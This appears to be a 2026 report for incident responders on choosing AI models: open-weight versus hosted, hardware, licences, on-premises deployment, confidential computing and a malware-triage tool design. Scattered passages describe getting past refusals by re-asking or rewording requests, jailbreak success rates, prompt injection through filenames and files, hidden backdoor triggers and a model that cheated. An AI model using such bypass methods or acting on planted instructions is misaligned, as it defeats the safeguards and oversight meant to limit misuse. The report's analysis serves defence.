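A few months can make a large difference in capability. On difficult security puzzles, CAISI scored GLM-5.2 at 39.3%, Claude Opus 4.8 at 48.4% and GPT-5.5 at 70.5%. On building exploits for known flaws in Chrome's JavaScript engine, GLM-5.2 scored 21.4%, Claude Opus 4.8 38.1% and GPT-5.5 40.7%. Kimi K3 did better than GLM-5.2 on the same exploit benchmark, but in 41 attempts it never achieved the most serious result, running code of its choice. The best closed models did so in about half of their attempts, according to UK AISI and CAISI's *UK AISI / CAISI Preliminary Assessment of Kimi K3's Cyber Capabilities*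 (2026).

These comparisons make hosted models look more useful to responders than they are, because the evaluators had the closed models' outer safeguards turned off. If a responder's tasks were as hard as CAISI's puzzles and refusals fell evenly across them, GLM-5.2 would complete more tasks than Opus 4.8 once Opus refused more than 19% of them (1 − 39.3/48.4). For GPT-5.5, the threshold is 44%. Opus 5.5's refusal rate in *CyberDualEval* was above both thresholds, but a team should use its own refusal rate in this calculation.

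None of these tests covers reading long logs, which is much of what responders want help with. The closest evidence is in Axios' *China's new open-source model accelerates AI hacking threat* (2026), which reports that the security company Graphistry found GLM-5.2 on par with leading American models at security investigations. Several open-weight models accept a million tokens at once, but they may still overlook an entry in the middle of the text.

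The gap between open and closed models probably matters little for explaining commands, building timelines or listing the places where programs start automatically. Mozilla's *The State of Open Source AI* (2026) estimates that both can handle jobs that would take a person less than eight hours. The gap matters more for analysing malware that resists analysis, following an intruder through many machines and writing exploits. The newest model may also be the wrong choice for writing an exploit to test a patch, because Moonshot deliberately reduced K3.1 Pro's ability to write working exploits before releasing it (Maier, *Kimi K3.1 Pro*, 2026).

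### Checking the licence and the files

Open-weight models have very different licence terms. GLM-5.2 has the MIT licence, which permits almost any use, according to noze's *GLM-5.3* (2026). Meta's Muse Spark Open, the strongest American open-weight model, has a custom licence with an acceptable use policy. Companies that make more than $20 million a month need a separate agreement to deploy it in some cases. *Meta shakes up the frontiers, open and closed* (Lambert, 2026) says the licence permits internal research and applications, which should cover the freight company investigating its own breach. A response firm that bills clients for the model's work should ask a lawyer whether the licence covers it. Both companies should save a copy of the licence with the model files, since the next version may have different terms.

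A model's name is weak evidence of what the download contains. In a joint report with another committee, the House Homeland Security Committee (2026) warned that anyone can adapt an open-weight model, rename it and build it into other products without disclosing where it came from. The team should download from the developer's own account and record the exact version and the checksum, a fingerprint calculated from a file's contents. A matching checksum shows that the file is the one the developer published, but not that the developer is trustworthy. Volunteers often publish compressed copies of popular models, and a team that uses such a copy has to trust the volunteer as well.

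Some model files can run code when a program loads them. The Hugging Face intrusion began with a dataset that ran code in this way. The safetensors format stores only the model's weights, so the team should prefer it and reject any model that needs the publisher's own code to start.

Download time is a reason to prepare early. At one byte per parameter, Muse Spark Open is 816 gigabytes, which would take about 18 hours to download on a 100-megabit-per-second office line.

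### Memory

A model needs memory roughly equal to its number of parameters times the bytes used to store each one, plus working memory for the text it is handling. Developers usually publish models at 16 or 8 bits (two bytes or one) per parameter. Compressing a model to 4 bits per parameter halves its 8-bit size, with some loss of accuracy.

| Model | Parameters | At 8 bits | At 4 bits |
|---|---|---|---|
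| Muse Glimmer | 30 billion | 30 GB | 15 GB |
| Muse Spark Open | 816 billion | 816 GB | 408 GB |
| Kimi K3 | 2.8 trillion | 2,800 GB | 1,400 GB |

Suppose Muse Spark Open needs another 100 GB of working memory for a few long conversations. At 8 bits, the total is 916 GB, which fits on a server with eight Nvidia H200 processors (141 GB each, 1,128 GB in total). At 4 bits, the total is 508 GB, and four H200s are enough. Kimi K3 needs a server with eight of the larger B300 processors even at 4 bits.

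Muse Spark Open's model card also lists 42 billion "active" parameters. The model uses only that many for each token, so it runs faster than its size suggests, but all 816 billion still have to be in memory. A buyer who sized the hardware from the smaller number would have a machine that can't load the model.

The active parameters help to estimate writing speed, because the machine has to read them from memory for every token. If a desktop computer reads 800 GB a second, it can write at most 19 tokens a second at 8 bits (800/42) or 38 at 4 bits. That is fast enough for one person asking questions, but too slow for a group of agents working through a breach.

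A small team could run Muse Glimmer at 4 bits on a single good graphics card. Epoch AI's *Open-weight models* includes a 2025 finding that models of this kind match the best closed models from a year or less earlier. That may be enough for routine tickets like the university's, though small models are easier to mislead with planted instructions. For something bigger, nextbigwhat's *Muse Spark Open* (2026) lists Muse Spark as optimised for Apple's M5 Ultra desktop computers but doesn't give a speed. A commenter on Hugging Face's disclosure thought four of Nvidia's small Spark machines would run GLM-5.2 well enough for forensic work. The commenter gave no measurements, so it would be sensible to borrow a machine for a day before buying four.

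### Time to read a log

Hugging Face had more than 17,000 recorded events to examine. If each event takes 400 tokens, the log contains about 6.8 million tokens. A machine that processes 1,500 tokens a second would need about 76 minutes to go through the log once, and one that processes 300 tokens a second would need more than six hours.

A log of that size is nearly seven times what fits in a million-token window, so the team has to divide it, and smaller pieces are usually safer. Dividing it into pieces of 50,000 tokens produces 136 of them. If the model writes 1,000 tokens of notes on each piece at 50 tokens a second, the writing adds 45 minutes. One reading is rarely enough, and separate readings for the timeline, the indicators, the stolen credentials and the decoys would bring the total to about eight hours if they ran one after another. A person could avoid most of this work by first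 using an ordinary search to remove duplicate and plainly irrelevant entries.

### Owned, rented and shared hardware

The table compares annual costs for a team that has one serious incident in the year. The prices for owned and rented machines are assumptions to replace with real quotes. The shared price comes from AISI's estimate that 100 million tokens cost about $46 with GLM-5.2, compared with $85 for Claude Opus 4.6.

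| Arrangement | What the team pays for | Cost in the year |
|---|---|---|
| Owned | A $400,000 server kept for four years, plus $40,000 a year for power and housing | $140,000 |
| Rented | The same server at $32 an hour, for a two-week incident and one eight-hour test a month | $13,800 |
| Shared | 50 readings of the 6.8-million-token log | $156 |

Owning the server is cheaper than renting one only if it is used for more than about 4,400 hours a year, or six months nonstop. A company that also uses the server for everyday alerts might reach that, but the freight company wouldn't.

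Shared hosting is the cheapest arrangement, but it sends breach data to another company, so the team has the same redaction and contract problems as with any hosted model. AISI's estimate also uses the advertised price of the developer, Z.ai, and sending evidence to Z.ai's own service would not keep it private. A server rented for the team's sole use is a reasonable compromise if one is available, but Cisco Talos warns that dedicated capacity is often scarce and that buying processors can take months. The rental contract should therefore reserve a machine, or at least state how quickly the supplier will provide one.

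None of these figures includes paying someone to keep the model working. For a small team, that may be the largest expense, and finding that person may be the hardest part to arrange at short notice.

### Keeping it away from the intruder

The machine running the model will hold the best record of what the responders know, so it shouldn't share a network, a cloud account or a login system with anything the intruder may have reached. At the freight company, that rules out joining it to the central directory, because the attacker already has one account there and may have more. The machine needs its own accounts, which responders use from clean laptops, and it should have no route to the internet. Responders can bring copies of the evidence to it on an encrypted drive.

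Written instructions aren't enough to limit what the model does. The security company Irregular tested GLM-5.3 in October and found that it repeatedly ignored instructions, according to AsiaOne's *Chinese AI model carries out complex cyberattacks in controlled tests, researchers say* (2026). The model also completed three of 13 multi-stage attacks at least once, the most of any open model Irregular has tested. An article by Pogorelec (2026) is headlined *Open-weight AI model GLM-5.3 cheated its way to correct answers*. A model that breaks rules to get an answer is risky to leave unsupervised with administrator rights.

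The operating system should enforce limits on what the model can do. The model's tools get read-only access to the evidence, a scratch folder to write in, and no working passwords. Each job has a time limit, and the machine records every command. If someone has to run the malware to see what it does, they use a separate, disposable machine. The model can draft a command for the company's live systems, but a person should read and run it.

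GLM-5.2 has some resistance to planted instructions. CAISI tried 31 publicly known ways to hijack an AI agent through emails, calendar entries and documents, and none worked. When CAISI searched automatically for new attacks, the model resisted longer than other open-weight models but not as long as the American closed ones.

### Testing it and keeping it current

Poor configuration can make a capable model perform badly. CAISI ran GLM-5.2 at 8-bit precision with the settings recommended by its developer, Z.ai, then checked the set-up by reproducing two of Z.ai's published benchmark results. Leaving out Z.ai's suggested prompt lowered mathematics scores by 5–10%. A team can check its own set-up the same way, and should repeat the check if it compresses the model to 4 bits.

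The team can then reuse the old cases from its refusal test, this time with known answers. To test how the model handles long logs, someone can place ten real attack entries at different points in a large log and count how many it finds. The team still needs to record refusals. AISI found that DeepSeek V4 Pro occasionally declined security tasks, mostly reverse engineering, and AISI got past these refusals by asking again. Meta gave Muse Spark Open extra safety training before releasing it, so it may refuse more often.

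Updating is fairly easy when a developer retrains a model without changing its structure. GLM-5.3 uses the same base model as GLM-5.2, so it should fit on the same hardware. Before switching, the team should run the old cases on both models, and it should keep the old model's files. No provider can withdraw those files, which is an advantage over hosted models. The software that runs the model needs security patches, and on an isolated machine somebody has to carry them over by hand.

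### Who decides what the model may do

David Bianco of Cisco Talos wants defenders to have "operational sovereignty", meaning the final say over what their AI may do. This differs from data sovereignty, which concerns where data is kept. He wants the defending organisation to set the model's safeguards, not remove them, so that a provider's change of policy can't suddenly disrupt its work. One of his proposals is a gateway that detects when a hosted model refuses a request and passes it to a smaller model the team controls. Another is a model that the companies in an industry pay for and govern together. The shared model would suit the freight company's budget, but every member would need it at once during an attack on the whole industry.

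The argument best supports keeping an open-weight model as a fallback. The evaluators still find closed models ahead by several months, and sometimes by a wide margin, which doesn't support Bianco's stronger claim that defenders increasingly accept restrictions without getting a more capable model in return. The published cases also don't establish his claim that state-sponsored attackers moved to self-hosted models after being banned by providers. He concedes that running a top model is unrealistic for most security teams.

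DeGrazia takes a more moderate position in *When Frontier Models Say No*. She teaches a course on local models for SANS, so she has an interest in their use, but she still recommends commercial models for some jobs. She adds that hosted services limit how much a customer can send in a given time, which favours local models because forensic work involves enormous amounts of data.

Security vendors are moving the same way. TechTarget's *Security vendors turn to multi-model, open AI to bypass guardrails* (2026) describes the Agentic SOC Alliance, a group of 15 vendors formed in July, whose proposed design lets customers replace the model without rebuilding the rest of the system. One vendor, ExtraHop, asked AI agents to investigate attacks on a known Windows flaw. Many models refused when the request named the flaw, but most completed the same job when the request instead described a server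 making connections it shouldn't. One model refused either way. Cisco has its own open-weight models, called Antares, according to The Next Web's *Open-weight AI caught the frontier on capability. On safety, it didn't*. A customer may therefore already have an open-weight model inside a product it bought, and should ask the vendor which model it is.

### Trust in Chinese-made models

Most of the strongest open-weight models are Chinese, and some organisations won't use them. Running one on an isolated machine prevents it from sending breach data to its developer, which is the most obvious danger, but its answers could still be skewed. A developer could train a model to behave normally until a particular phrase appears in its input, which ordinary tests would be unlikely to include.

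The House committees concluded in November that Chinese models can differ from others in ways that ordinary evaluations may miss. They relied partly on classified briefings, which outsiders can't check, and they want American companies to have an American alternative. Some differences are already public. CAISI found that Kimi K2 Thinking, an older Moonshot model, censored its answers heavily in Chinese but very little in English. This suggests that a model's behaviour can depend on the language of the question, but it doesn't come close to showing that a model would hide an intrusion.

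The evidence against a hidden trigger is also limited. Hugging Face used GLM-5.2 on a real breach and reported no sabotage, and CAISI found the model harder to hijack than other open-weight models, but neither was looking for a hidden trigger. Developers' disclosures don't rule one out for any country's models. Mozilla examined 16 notable open releases and found that none came with full information about its training data.

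A response team can test for the bias that would hurt it most, which is a model changing its findings depending on who seems responsible for an attack. The team runs the model on an old case, changes only the details that suggest who was responsible, such as the language of comments in the malware, then runs it again and compares the findings. Matching findings don't rule out bias triggered by other details. Before declaring a machine safe, the team should also try a model from a different developer if it can.

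A company that avoids Chinese models now gives up less capability than it used to. Lambert places Muse Spark Open above GLM-5.2 in general ability and behind GLM-5.3 and Kimi K3. A company with government contracts may prefer it anyway, because GLM's developer, Z.ai, is on the US Commerce Department's Entity List, which restricts exports to the companies on it. The company's lawyers would have to judge whether using a free download of a Z.ai model causes any difficulty.

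### Whether any of this helps attackers

Releasing a capable model can help attackers. Ament, Edelman and Barry (2026), in *AI can turn public security fixes into working exploits*, describe how GLM-5.3 produced working exploits for six versions of Firefox, for about $1,000 each, from fixes that Mozilla had published but not yet sent to users. Fasano, Fleischer and colleagues (2026), in *GLM-5.3 and the spread of advanced cyber capabilities*, used simple techniques to get past the model's safeguards in 64% to 100% of simulated attempts. They work for Anthropic, which competes with Z.ai, the model's developer, but they acknowledge that defenders can benefit from the model. The House committees estimate that removing its safeguards costs a few thousand dollars.

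The first open-weight model to reach a given level of ability helps attackers the most. A second one of similar ability adds much less, because attackers can already download the first. The developer can't take back a model after releasing it, but can weaken a dangerous skill beforehand. Moonshot did this with K3.1 Pro, though AISI's results suggest that the model remained very capable of attacking networks. Defenders with access to a closed model can also use the months before an open equivalent is released to fix flaws.

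A responder who downloads GLM-5.3 gives attackers no added capability, because they can already get the same files. Wide use by defenders might encourage developers to release more models, but one response team would add very little to that effect.

A defender can still accidentally give a thief more than the public download offers, either by training the model further on its own collection of exploits or by building software around it that makes it much better at breaking into systems. The team should guard such additions from theft as it would guard its exploits. It should also shut the server down between tests, so that an intruder can't use it as UNC6508 used its victims' cloud systems.

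## Installing a vendor's model on the customer's premises

Some vendors install a model whose parameters they keep secret in the customer's data centre or in a cloud run by a local operator. The breach data stays on site, as with an open-weight model, and the vendor still tries to control who can copy the model. Google sells its Gemini models this way, and the French AI company Mistral and the Canadian AI company Cohere sell theirs the same way.

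A buyer needs to ask four questions: where the machine is, who can read the data, who can copy the parameters, and who can change the safeguards or watch how people use the model. Sales material often doesn't distinguish between them. In 2025, for example, Microsoft let customers move its interface to OpenAI's models closer to their data but had no on-premises version of the service, according to TechTarget's *Google Gemini 2.5 Pro extends on-prem GenAI support*. OpenAI (2026) announced a partnership with the computer maker Dell to bring its coding tool Codex to "on-premises enterprise environments". A buyer should ask where the model itself runs, because a tool can work on local files while sending every prompt to a remote server.

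### What vendors offered in late 2026

Google sells Gemini on Google Distributed Cloud, which comes in two versions. The air-gapped version has no outside connection and runs on hardware that Google supplies, according to *New innovations in Google Distributed Cloud* (Sambi, 2026). With the connected version, Google manages the software on hardware the customer owns. Shirodkar, a Google vice president, says US agencies may use the air-gapped version for Secret and Top Secret work.

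The installed models are older than the hosted ones. In late October 2026, Google's air-gapped cloud offered Gemini 3.5 Flash, part of Google's line of faster, cheaper models, for general use (Lagonsin, 2026, *Google adds AI & partner tools to air-gapped cloud*). That model was two releases and at least three months behind. Google had announced 3.6 Flash on July 21 (Doshi, 2026, *Introducing Gemini 3.6 Flash, 3.5 Flash-Lite, and 3.5 Flash Cyber*) and had released 3.8 Flash by early September. In the same week as the air-gapped update, it also launched a new hosted flagship (Deutscher, 2026, *Google debuts flagship Gemini 4 Carbon model with cybersecurity upgrades*).

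The connected version may lag further. Sambi announced a preview of the latest Flash models for it in April, but in June Google Cloud's documentation still listed only Gemini 2.5 Flash. Google planned to retire the hosted version of that model on October 16, according to its *Vertex AI release notes*. A customer who ordered the documented set-up in summer might have been installing a model that Google planned to drop from its own cloud within months.

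Security patches also take longer to reach a disconnected machine. An air-gapped release that Google Cloud (2026) announced on January 26 contained an operating system image from December 10, so the image was already 47 days old, and customers still had to bring it on site.

Google Cloud Dedicated, a separate product, is a cloud that a local company runs under local law. In Europe, Google relies on Thales, S3NS and other partners to run it, according to LeMagIT's *Cloud « souverain »* (2026). The partner approves whatever enters or leaves, including software updates, and Google Cloud says its standard operators have no direct access. Google plans to add Gemini but hasn't given a date, according to 葉's *Google 將 Gemini 引進主權雲 斷網仍可獨立運作一年* (2026). The partner could keep the cloud running for up to 12 months without connecting to Google. Customers can hold the main encryption keys outside Google's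 systems, but they should still ask what the partner's staff can see.

Cohere gives the customer more control. Cohere's *Private Deployment Overview* says the customer buys and runs the hardware, with guidance from Cohere. In *Private deployments*, the company promises that it has "zero access to the data you process" and says set-up usually takes less than a day once the contract is signed. The customer downloads the model as a container, a package of software ready to run, and Cohere tells customers they can "replicate this image anywhere you want". A response team can therefore put a second copy on a clean network, but this freedom also suggests that the licence and the customer's own security are the main safeguards against unauthorised copying.

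Mistral offers both open-weight and proprietary models, and installation rights vary by model, according to MintMCP, a software vendor. Mistral's flagship model, Mistral Large 3, is open-weight, so a customer can install the same model that Mistral hosts. A customer who pays for a private deployment of it gets support and integration, but not exclusive access. Mistral also offers air-gapped installation through the data company Cloudera.

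| Arrangement | Where the machine stands | Who can read the data | Who can copy the parameters | Who controls the safeguards |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Hosted model | Provider's or cloud company's site | Customer, and the provider within its retention terms | Provider | Provider |
| Gemini, connected | Customer's site | Customer | Google; encryption is meant to stop the customer | Google, which manages the software |
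| Gemini, air-gapped | Customer's site | Customer and its operators | Google; encryption is meant to stop the customer | Google sets them in each release, but can't watch their use |
| Google Cloud Dedicated (Gemini planned) | Local partner's site | Customer; the partner's access depends on the keys | Not yet clear | Google writes updates, and the partner can block them |
| Cohere private deployment | Customer's site or private cloud | Customer | Customer's administrators, within the licence | Mostly the customer, who can retrain the model |
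| Open-weight model | Customer's site | Customer | Anyone | Customer |

### How a vendor can keep parameters secret on a customer's machine

Someone who administers an ordinary server can copy anything in its memory, including a model's parameters. To prevent this, vendors can use confidential computing and remote attestation, the same techniques that Tetali proposes for guarding customers' conversations. A typical design works like this:

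1. The vendor encrypts the parameters and puts the encrypted file on the server. The customer can copy the file but has no key to open it.
2. The server's processor starts a confidential virtual machine, a sealed-off computer within the computer. It encrypts that machine's memory with a key that stays inside the chip, so an administrator who copies the memory gets unreadable data. The graphics processors that run the model need a similar protected mode.
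3. The processor calculates a fingerprint of the software it has loaded and signs it with a secret key that the chip's manufacturer vouches for.
4. The vendor's server checks the signature and compares the fingerprint with a list of approved software. If the customer had changed the software to save the parameters to a disk, the fingerprint would be different.
5. If everything matches, the vendor sends the decryption key over an encrypted connection that ends inside the confidential virtual machine. The parameters are readable only there.

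Google uses confidential virtual machines and remote attestation in the connected version to protect "model weights and prompt data", according to Google Cloud's *Gemini on Google Distributed Cloud connected API documentation*. The server has to stay in contact with Google, and if it loses contact for more than 30 minutes, the virtual machines shut down until contact is restored.

Under that rule, if the freight company cut its internet connection during a breach to stop the intruder from copying files, it would lose the model half an hour later. A team using the connected version needs a separate internet line for the model's server and should test whether the model keeps running when the main network is off.

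An air-gapped server can't contact the vendor in step 4. Instead, the checking system can be put on site, or the vendor can store the key in a chip that releases it only to approved software. With either method, the vendor can't refuse to unlock the model later unless it has built in an expiry date or can return to the site.

### What encrypted memory leaves exposed

Attestation shows which software is running, but that software may still have a flaw that lets someone access the model's parameters. Encrypted memory protects breach data only inside the virtual machine, so an intruder on the responder's laptop could read the data before it goes in and the answer after it comes out.

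The intruder could also use the model. The preview of the connected version couldn't identify individual users, according to Google Cloud's *Gemini on Google Distributed Cloud connected API release notes* (2025). Requests went through a service account (an identity meant for software) with keys that expired after 14 days. Someone who stole a key could have sent prompts that looked like the team's. Google has since announced a gateway that logs every request to the model, but the team still has to read the log and work out who sent each request.

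The customer's physical control of the server is a harder problem. In October 2025, academic researchers published TEE.fail, an attack that uses a device costing less than $1,000 to read the traffic between a server's processor and its DDR5 memory. They recovered keys used to sign attestations on Intel processors, and keys from software running inside a confidential virtual machine on AMD processors. With a stolen attestation key, an attacker could forge the report in step 3 and might persuade a vendor to unlock the parameters on an unprotected machine. Intel and AMD don't promise protection against such attacks, so cameras, locks and tamper seals still matter. Google's certified server has an Intel processor and DDR5 memory, but the researchers didn't test Google's product, and Google also records the identity of each server.

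Encrypted memory can't prevent distillation either, because the customer has to be able to read the model's answers.

### Misuse without a connection

A vendor can't monitor an air-gapped model or suspend its users. When customers hold the records for OpenAI's hosted models, the company still gets a limited warning, but a disconnected server sends nothing. Local logs help an honest customer catch a dishonest employee, but they are little use against a customer who wants to attack other people, since that customer controls them.

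Running a model disconnected from its vendor can help responders. SiliconANGLE (2026) reported that the US government forced Anthropic to take Mythos offline in June. A disconnected copy would have kept running, though the customer might still have had a legal duty to stop using it. But the vendor also can't switch off a disconnected copy if it is stolen, or if the vendor later decides it shouldn't have supplied that customer.

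The vendor therefore has to do most of its checking before delivery. Checks fit fairly naturally into the setup of Google's connected version, because the customer must order a particular server, give Google its identification details and wait for a Google technician to install the software. A criminal could set up a company and do all that, but it would cost far more than using a stolen API key. Contracts can add inspections, a duty to keep logs and a ban on moving the model, though they work best on customers with a reputation and assets to lose.

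Even a well-chosen customer can leak a model. In January 2024 a Mistral model appeared on Hugging Face under the name "miqu". Mistral's chief executive, Arthur Mensch, said that an employee of an early customer had leaked a compressed, watermarked copy of an older model. A watermark may help a vendor trace a leak, but the vendor still can't retrieve the leaked files.

### Stolen accounts and stolen parameters

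If someone steals an account for a hosted model, the provider can cancel it, and the provider's safeguards still apply to each request until then. Someone who steals a model's readable parameters can use them indefinitely, retrain the model to stop refusing, and pass copies to others. The thief needs suitable hardware but can rent it.

An invented example compares the risks of hosted accounts and an installed model. Suppose a team of 75 people has one hosted account each, every account has a 0.2% chance of being stolen in a year, and a thief keeps a stolen account for three weeks. Thieves would get an average of about three days' use a year (75 × 0.002 × 21 = 3.15). Now suppose the team uses an installed model instead, and someone steals the parameters and shares them with ten criminal groups. If each group uses them for 150 days before an equally good open-weight model appears, attackers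 get 1,500 days' use. Measured by average days of attacker use, the installed model would be safer only if the yearly chance of such a theft were below about 0.2% (3.15 ÷ 1,500), or one in 476.

The result depends heavily on the number of groups and the 150 days, and it treats every day of use as equally harmful. A day of use with stolen parameters is probably more harmful, because nobody is monitoring it.

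The age of the model could matter more than any of this. Once attackers can download an equally capable open-weight model, stealing the vendor's model gives them almost no extra capability. Open-weight models have recently been several months behind closed ones on security work, so they have probably overtaken Gemini 2.5 Flash already. Losing its parameters would hurt Google commercially but add little to what attackers can do. Losing those of Gemini 4 Carbon or a Mythos model could be much more serious. Installed models lag behind the newest ones, which makes them less useful to responders but safer to install. A vendor that shortens this delay will need to protect the parameters better.

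### Cost and refusals

Google's documented connected set-up needs a Dell server with eight H200 processors. On the previous section's assumptions, a server of that size costs about $140,000 a year to own and run, before Google's own charges. A bank, a defence agency or a large response firm could realistically pay that, but the freight company could hardly do so. Cohere's workplace assistant, North, can run on as few as two graphics processors, according to Dataconomy, though a small installation would handle fewer long logs at once. StorageNewsletter's *Cirrascale Expands Model Offerings to Include Gemini on Google Distributed Cloud* reports that the cloud company Cirrascale also sells Gemini in connected and air-gapped forms. The four questions apply again to anyone using a supplier's machine, because the supplier may have physical access to it.

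Lagonsin reports that the air-gapped version of Google's platform now works with Elastic Security, which collects logs and detects threats on individual machines. This suits responders well because the logs and the model can stay on the same isolated platform. The same update included a preview of a search tool that lets users question Gemini about an organisation's documents, recordings and videos. The tool should respect each user's existing permissions, because an intruder with a valid login might also find it useful.

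None of these offers explicitly includes looser cyber safeguards. Google does make security models. *Introducing Gemini 3.5 Flash Cyber* (Popa and Flynn, 2026) describes one for finding, validating and patching flaws, and *Google releases Gemini 3.8 Flash and a cybersecurity variant limited to governments* (Constantin, 2026) reports that Google limited a later version to governments. But the air-gapped model that Lagonsin describes is the ordinary 3.5 Flash.

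Moving a model on site doesn't remove its trained refusals, which are part of the parameters. Without a connection, the vendor can't monitor the customer's account, but it may install its own filters. Google says its platform includes tools that block harmful content. An installed model could therefore refuse more or less than the hosted one. Before signing, a response team should run its refusal test on the exact version it would receive and ask whether it may turn off the filters or retrain the model. If it may do neither, the team could spend $140,000 a year and still be unable to get the safeguards loosened during a weekend incident because nobody at the vendor is available to do it.

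## Using tools limited to one task

The freight company could hardly afford an installed Gemini server, and its responder mostly needs answers, not free use of a model. A tool limited to one task provides only those answers. Someone uploads a suspicious file, a model examines it in the background, and the tool returns a short report. Because the buyer never types a prompt, the maker can use a model with looser safeguards without giving the buyer free use of it.

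Limiting a tool to one task works because responders and attackers often want different things from the same analysis. A tool can describe in detail what a piece of malware does and how to find it on other machines, which is what a responder wants, without writing the working malware that an attacker usually wants.

### Designing a malware-triage tool

Suppose a security company builds a tool to triage files like the program left on the freight company's server, which means deciding which files are harmless, which are malicious and which need an expert. The tool accepts one file and returns a verdict, the malware's family (the named group of related programs it belongs to), its behaviour and indicators of compromise, and a detection rule that other security software can use to search for it. It does not return working code.

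The upload page limits the file's size and has no box for questions, but a filename can still carry a message to the model. Choi (2026), in *MARS*, describes an experimental triage system that normally replaces filenames with neutral labels.

The instruction to the model also stays the same for every file, and only the record of the program's behaviour changes. *Trident* (2026) includes two such instructions. With the first, the model uses the record to judge whether the program is malicious and explains why. With the second, it writes detection rules general enough to catch similar malware but specific enough not to flag ordinary software.

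But the file can contain a prompt injection. An attacker could buy the tool, hide a request for new malware inside an ordinary program, and upload it. Choi's system marks file contents as untrusted and tells the model not to follow instructions in them. David C of the UK National Cyber Security Centre explains in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* that such markings make prompt injection harder but can't rule it out, because nothing inside a model firmly separates instructions from data.

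The maker therefore has to use ordinary software to limit what the model can do. *TRIAGE-CPG* (Sava, Küchler and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that gives the model few options. Software breaks the program into functions, its small working parts, and selects up to 75 for the model to read. The model can then read up to 30 more, list which functions call each other, search for those that use a particular Windows feature, or stop. When it stops, the software freezes the evidence, and a separate step writes the report without opening any more code.

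Nothing in that system runs the malware. For tools that do run it, *AI-Assisted Malware Analysis Tips* (Zeltser, 2026) recommends putting the AI agent inside an isolated lab with only the connections the agent needs. For deciding what else to allow, David C passes on the rule that a model reading a stranger's text should have no more privileges than the stranger, who in this case is the malware's author.

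The model then fills in a form. Choi tested a strict version in which the model lists claims about the file, gives each one a category and a severity from 1 to 5, and leaves the verdict to a fixed formula. On 1,195 programs, asking for a verdict directly was more accurate with all six models, by 3.7 to 20.9 percentage points. But with the form, anyone can recalculate a stored verdict, or apply a revised formula, without calling the model again. Choi did so for two models that their provider had since withdrawn. A tool could ask for a direct verdict and collect the claims separately. The claims wouldn't explain how the model reached its verdict, but if someone asks months later why the company declared a server clean, there would be a record of what the model reported.

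Before the tool returns its report, a filter checks every field. It rejects any verdict outside the permitted list, removes addresses that appear in neither the file nor its recorded traffic, and strips comments from the detection rule because they could contain code. The plain-language summary is the hardest field to check because it can contain any text. The tool's maker can limit its length and block any summary that contains code.

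The filter should also test the detection rule. In *Threat Hunting to Detection Engineering, Part 2*, Botelho (2026) had Claude write eight rules from its analysis of a malware sample. Four didn't fire when the malware ran. After Claude corrected them, all eight did. Botelho works for a security vendor and tried only one sample, but the failures are a good reason to run each rule against the malware and a collection of harmless programs before anyone relies on it.

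The tool also logs inputs, outputs and each action the model attempts. David C recommends logging failed actions too, because an attacker will probably need several tries to make a planted instruction work.

### How well it would sort files

Sava and colleagues tested their system with eight models on 600 Windows programs, half of them malware. The best model, Gemini 3.1 Pro, labeled 65% of the malware malicious and another 12% suspicious, so it missed about 23%. It correctly labeled 94% of the harmless programs.

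If the freight company submitted 100 files, five of them malicious, the tool would label about ten as malicious or suspicious. Four of those would be real malware, and the fifth malicious file would probably be among the 90 labeled benign, so a "benign" label is a weak reason to stop investigating a machine that an intruder has used.

Among the largest fifth of files, Gemini 3.1 Pro labeled only 33% of the malware malicious. The models often labeled malware suspicious rather than malicious when it was inside a wrapper, such as an installer or a packer that scrambles the program until it runs, because the wrapper hid the malicious code. The tool should send wrapped files to a person or a lab that can unpack them.

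The fields also differ in reliability. Depending on the model, the behaviour described in the reports matched outside threat intelligence for 75–96% of the malware, but the family name matched for only 1–6%. These figures are approximate because another model judged the matches. Family names depend on vendors' naming habits and on knowledge of past attacks, neither of which is in the code. A sensible tool would look up the family in a database of known malware and leave the field blank if it found no match.

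### What an attacker could learn from each field

| Field | What a responder gains | What an attacker who buys the tool gains |
|---|---|---|
| Verdict | A reason to investigate further or move on | A test of whether defenders would catch the attacker's own malware |
| Family | A link to earlier attacks | A warning that investigators could connect the malware to the attacker's past work |
| Behaviour | A list of damage to look for | Ideas from other people's malware, and a list of what defenders notice in the attacker's own |
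| Indicators | Addresses and files to search for elsewhere | A list of things to replace before attacking |
| Detection rule | A way to find other copies | The exact features to change to avoid detection |

None of the fields gives the attacker a working program, but together they are a good guide to hiding one. Criminals already pay for much less help than that. According to TechRadar's *FBI, Secret Service operation takes down AVCheck site used to test malware*, AVCheck let them test malware against several antivirus products before using it, without raising alarms. The service was useful to them even without explanations of the results. A triage tool that returns its reasons and a detection rule would help them more, at least in evading detection at other customers of the same tool.

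An attacker's chance of getting malware cleared rises quickly with the number of attempts. Suppose each new version has an independent 23% chance of a "benign" verdict, the rate at which Gemini 3.1 Pro cleared malware. The chance of getting at least one version cleared is then 41% with two attempts and 93% with ten. The real chances are probably lower for careless changes, because versions of the same program tend to get the same verdict, but an attacker who can read the detection rule will choose changes carefully.

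The maker can look for this pattern. Security Affairs' *Analyze VirusTotal Metadata to profile hackers* describes how a researcher named Dixon spent years tracking files submitted to VirusTotal, a service that checks them with many scanners. From the records of these submissions, Dixon could see suspected Chinese and Iranian groups adjusting their malware over weeks and months as fewer scanners detected it, and could sometimes predict when they would attack.

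Responders, however, often want no lasting record. A file from a breach may contain passwords or a client's name, and an attacker who finds it on a public service learns that someone has discovered the intrusion. The tool's maker could delete the file and keep only a similarity fingerprint, a short code that is nearly the same for nearly identical files. It could then return results automatically for, say, the first three similar files from one customer and have a person review the rest. Most responders would seldom reach the limit, but a victim of GTG-20006, the Russian group that kept rebuilding its malware, might reach it in an hour, so the reviewer has to be available at weekends.

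The maker could also send the detection rule straight to the customer's security software without showing anyone its text. Attackers would learn less, though they could still buy the software and test against it. Responders would be unable to read the rule and check it for mistakes.

### How Anthropic and OpenAI apply the idea

Anthropic sorts what a verified company offers its own customers into three types, according to who directs the model.

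| Type | Who directs Claude | What the customer receives | Status |
|---|---|---|---|
| Managed service | The seller's staff | Finished work that the staff have reviewed | Open to applications |
| Constrained product | The seller's product | Results, without the model's raw output | Open to applications, for Defense Access only |
| Unconstrained product | The customer, in the typical case | Potentially the model's own answers | Not yet available |

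The triage tool would probably be a constrained product. Its maker should ask Anthropic whether a summary counts as raw output if Claude wrote it and the filter passed it unchanged. Constrained products are limited to Defense Access, so they can't use the exploit development that Red Team Access permits.

A company that wants to build Daybreak into a product for others has to join OpenAI's partner programme. Besides managed services, the programme covers products with what OpenAI calls "bounded product workflows and curated outputs". According to OpenAI's *Putting frontier cyber models in more trusted hands* (2026), the partner has access to the model, but the customer does not.

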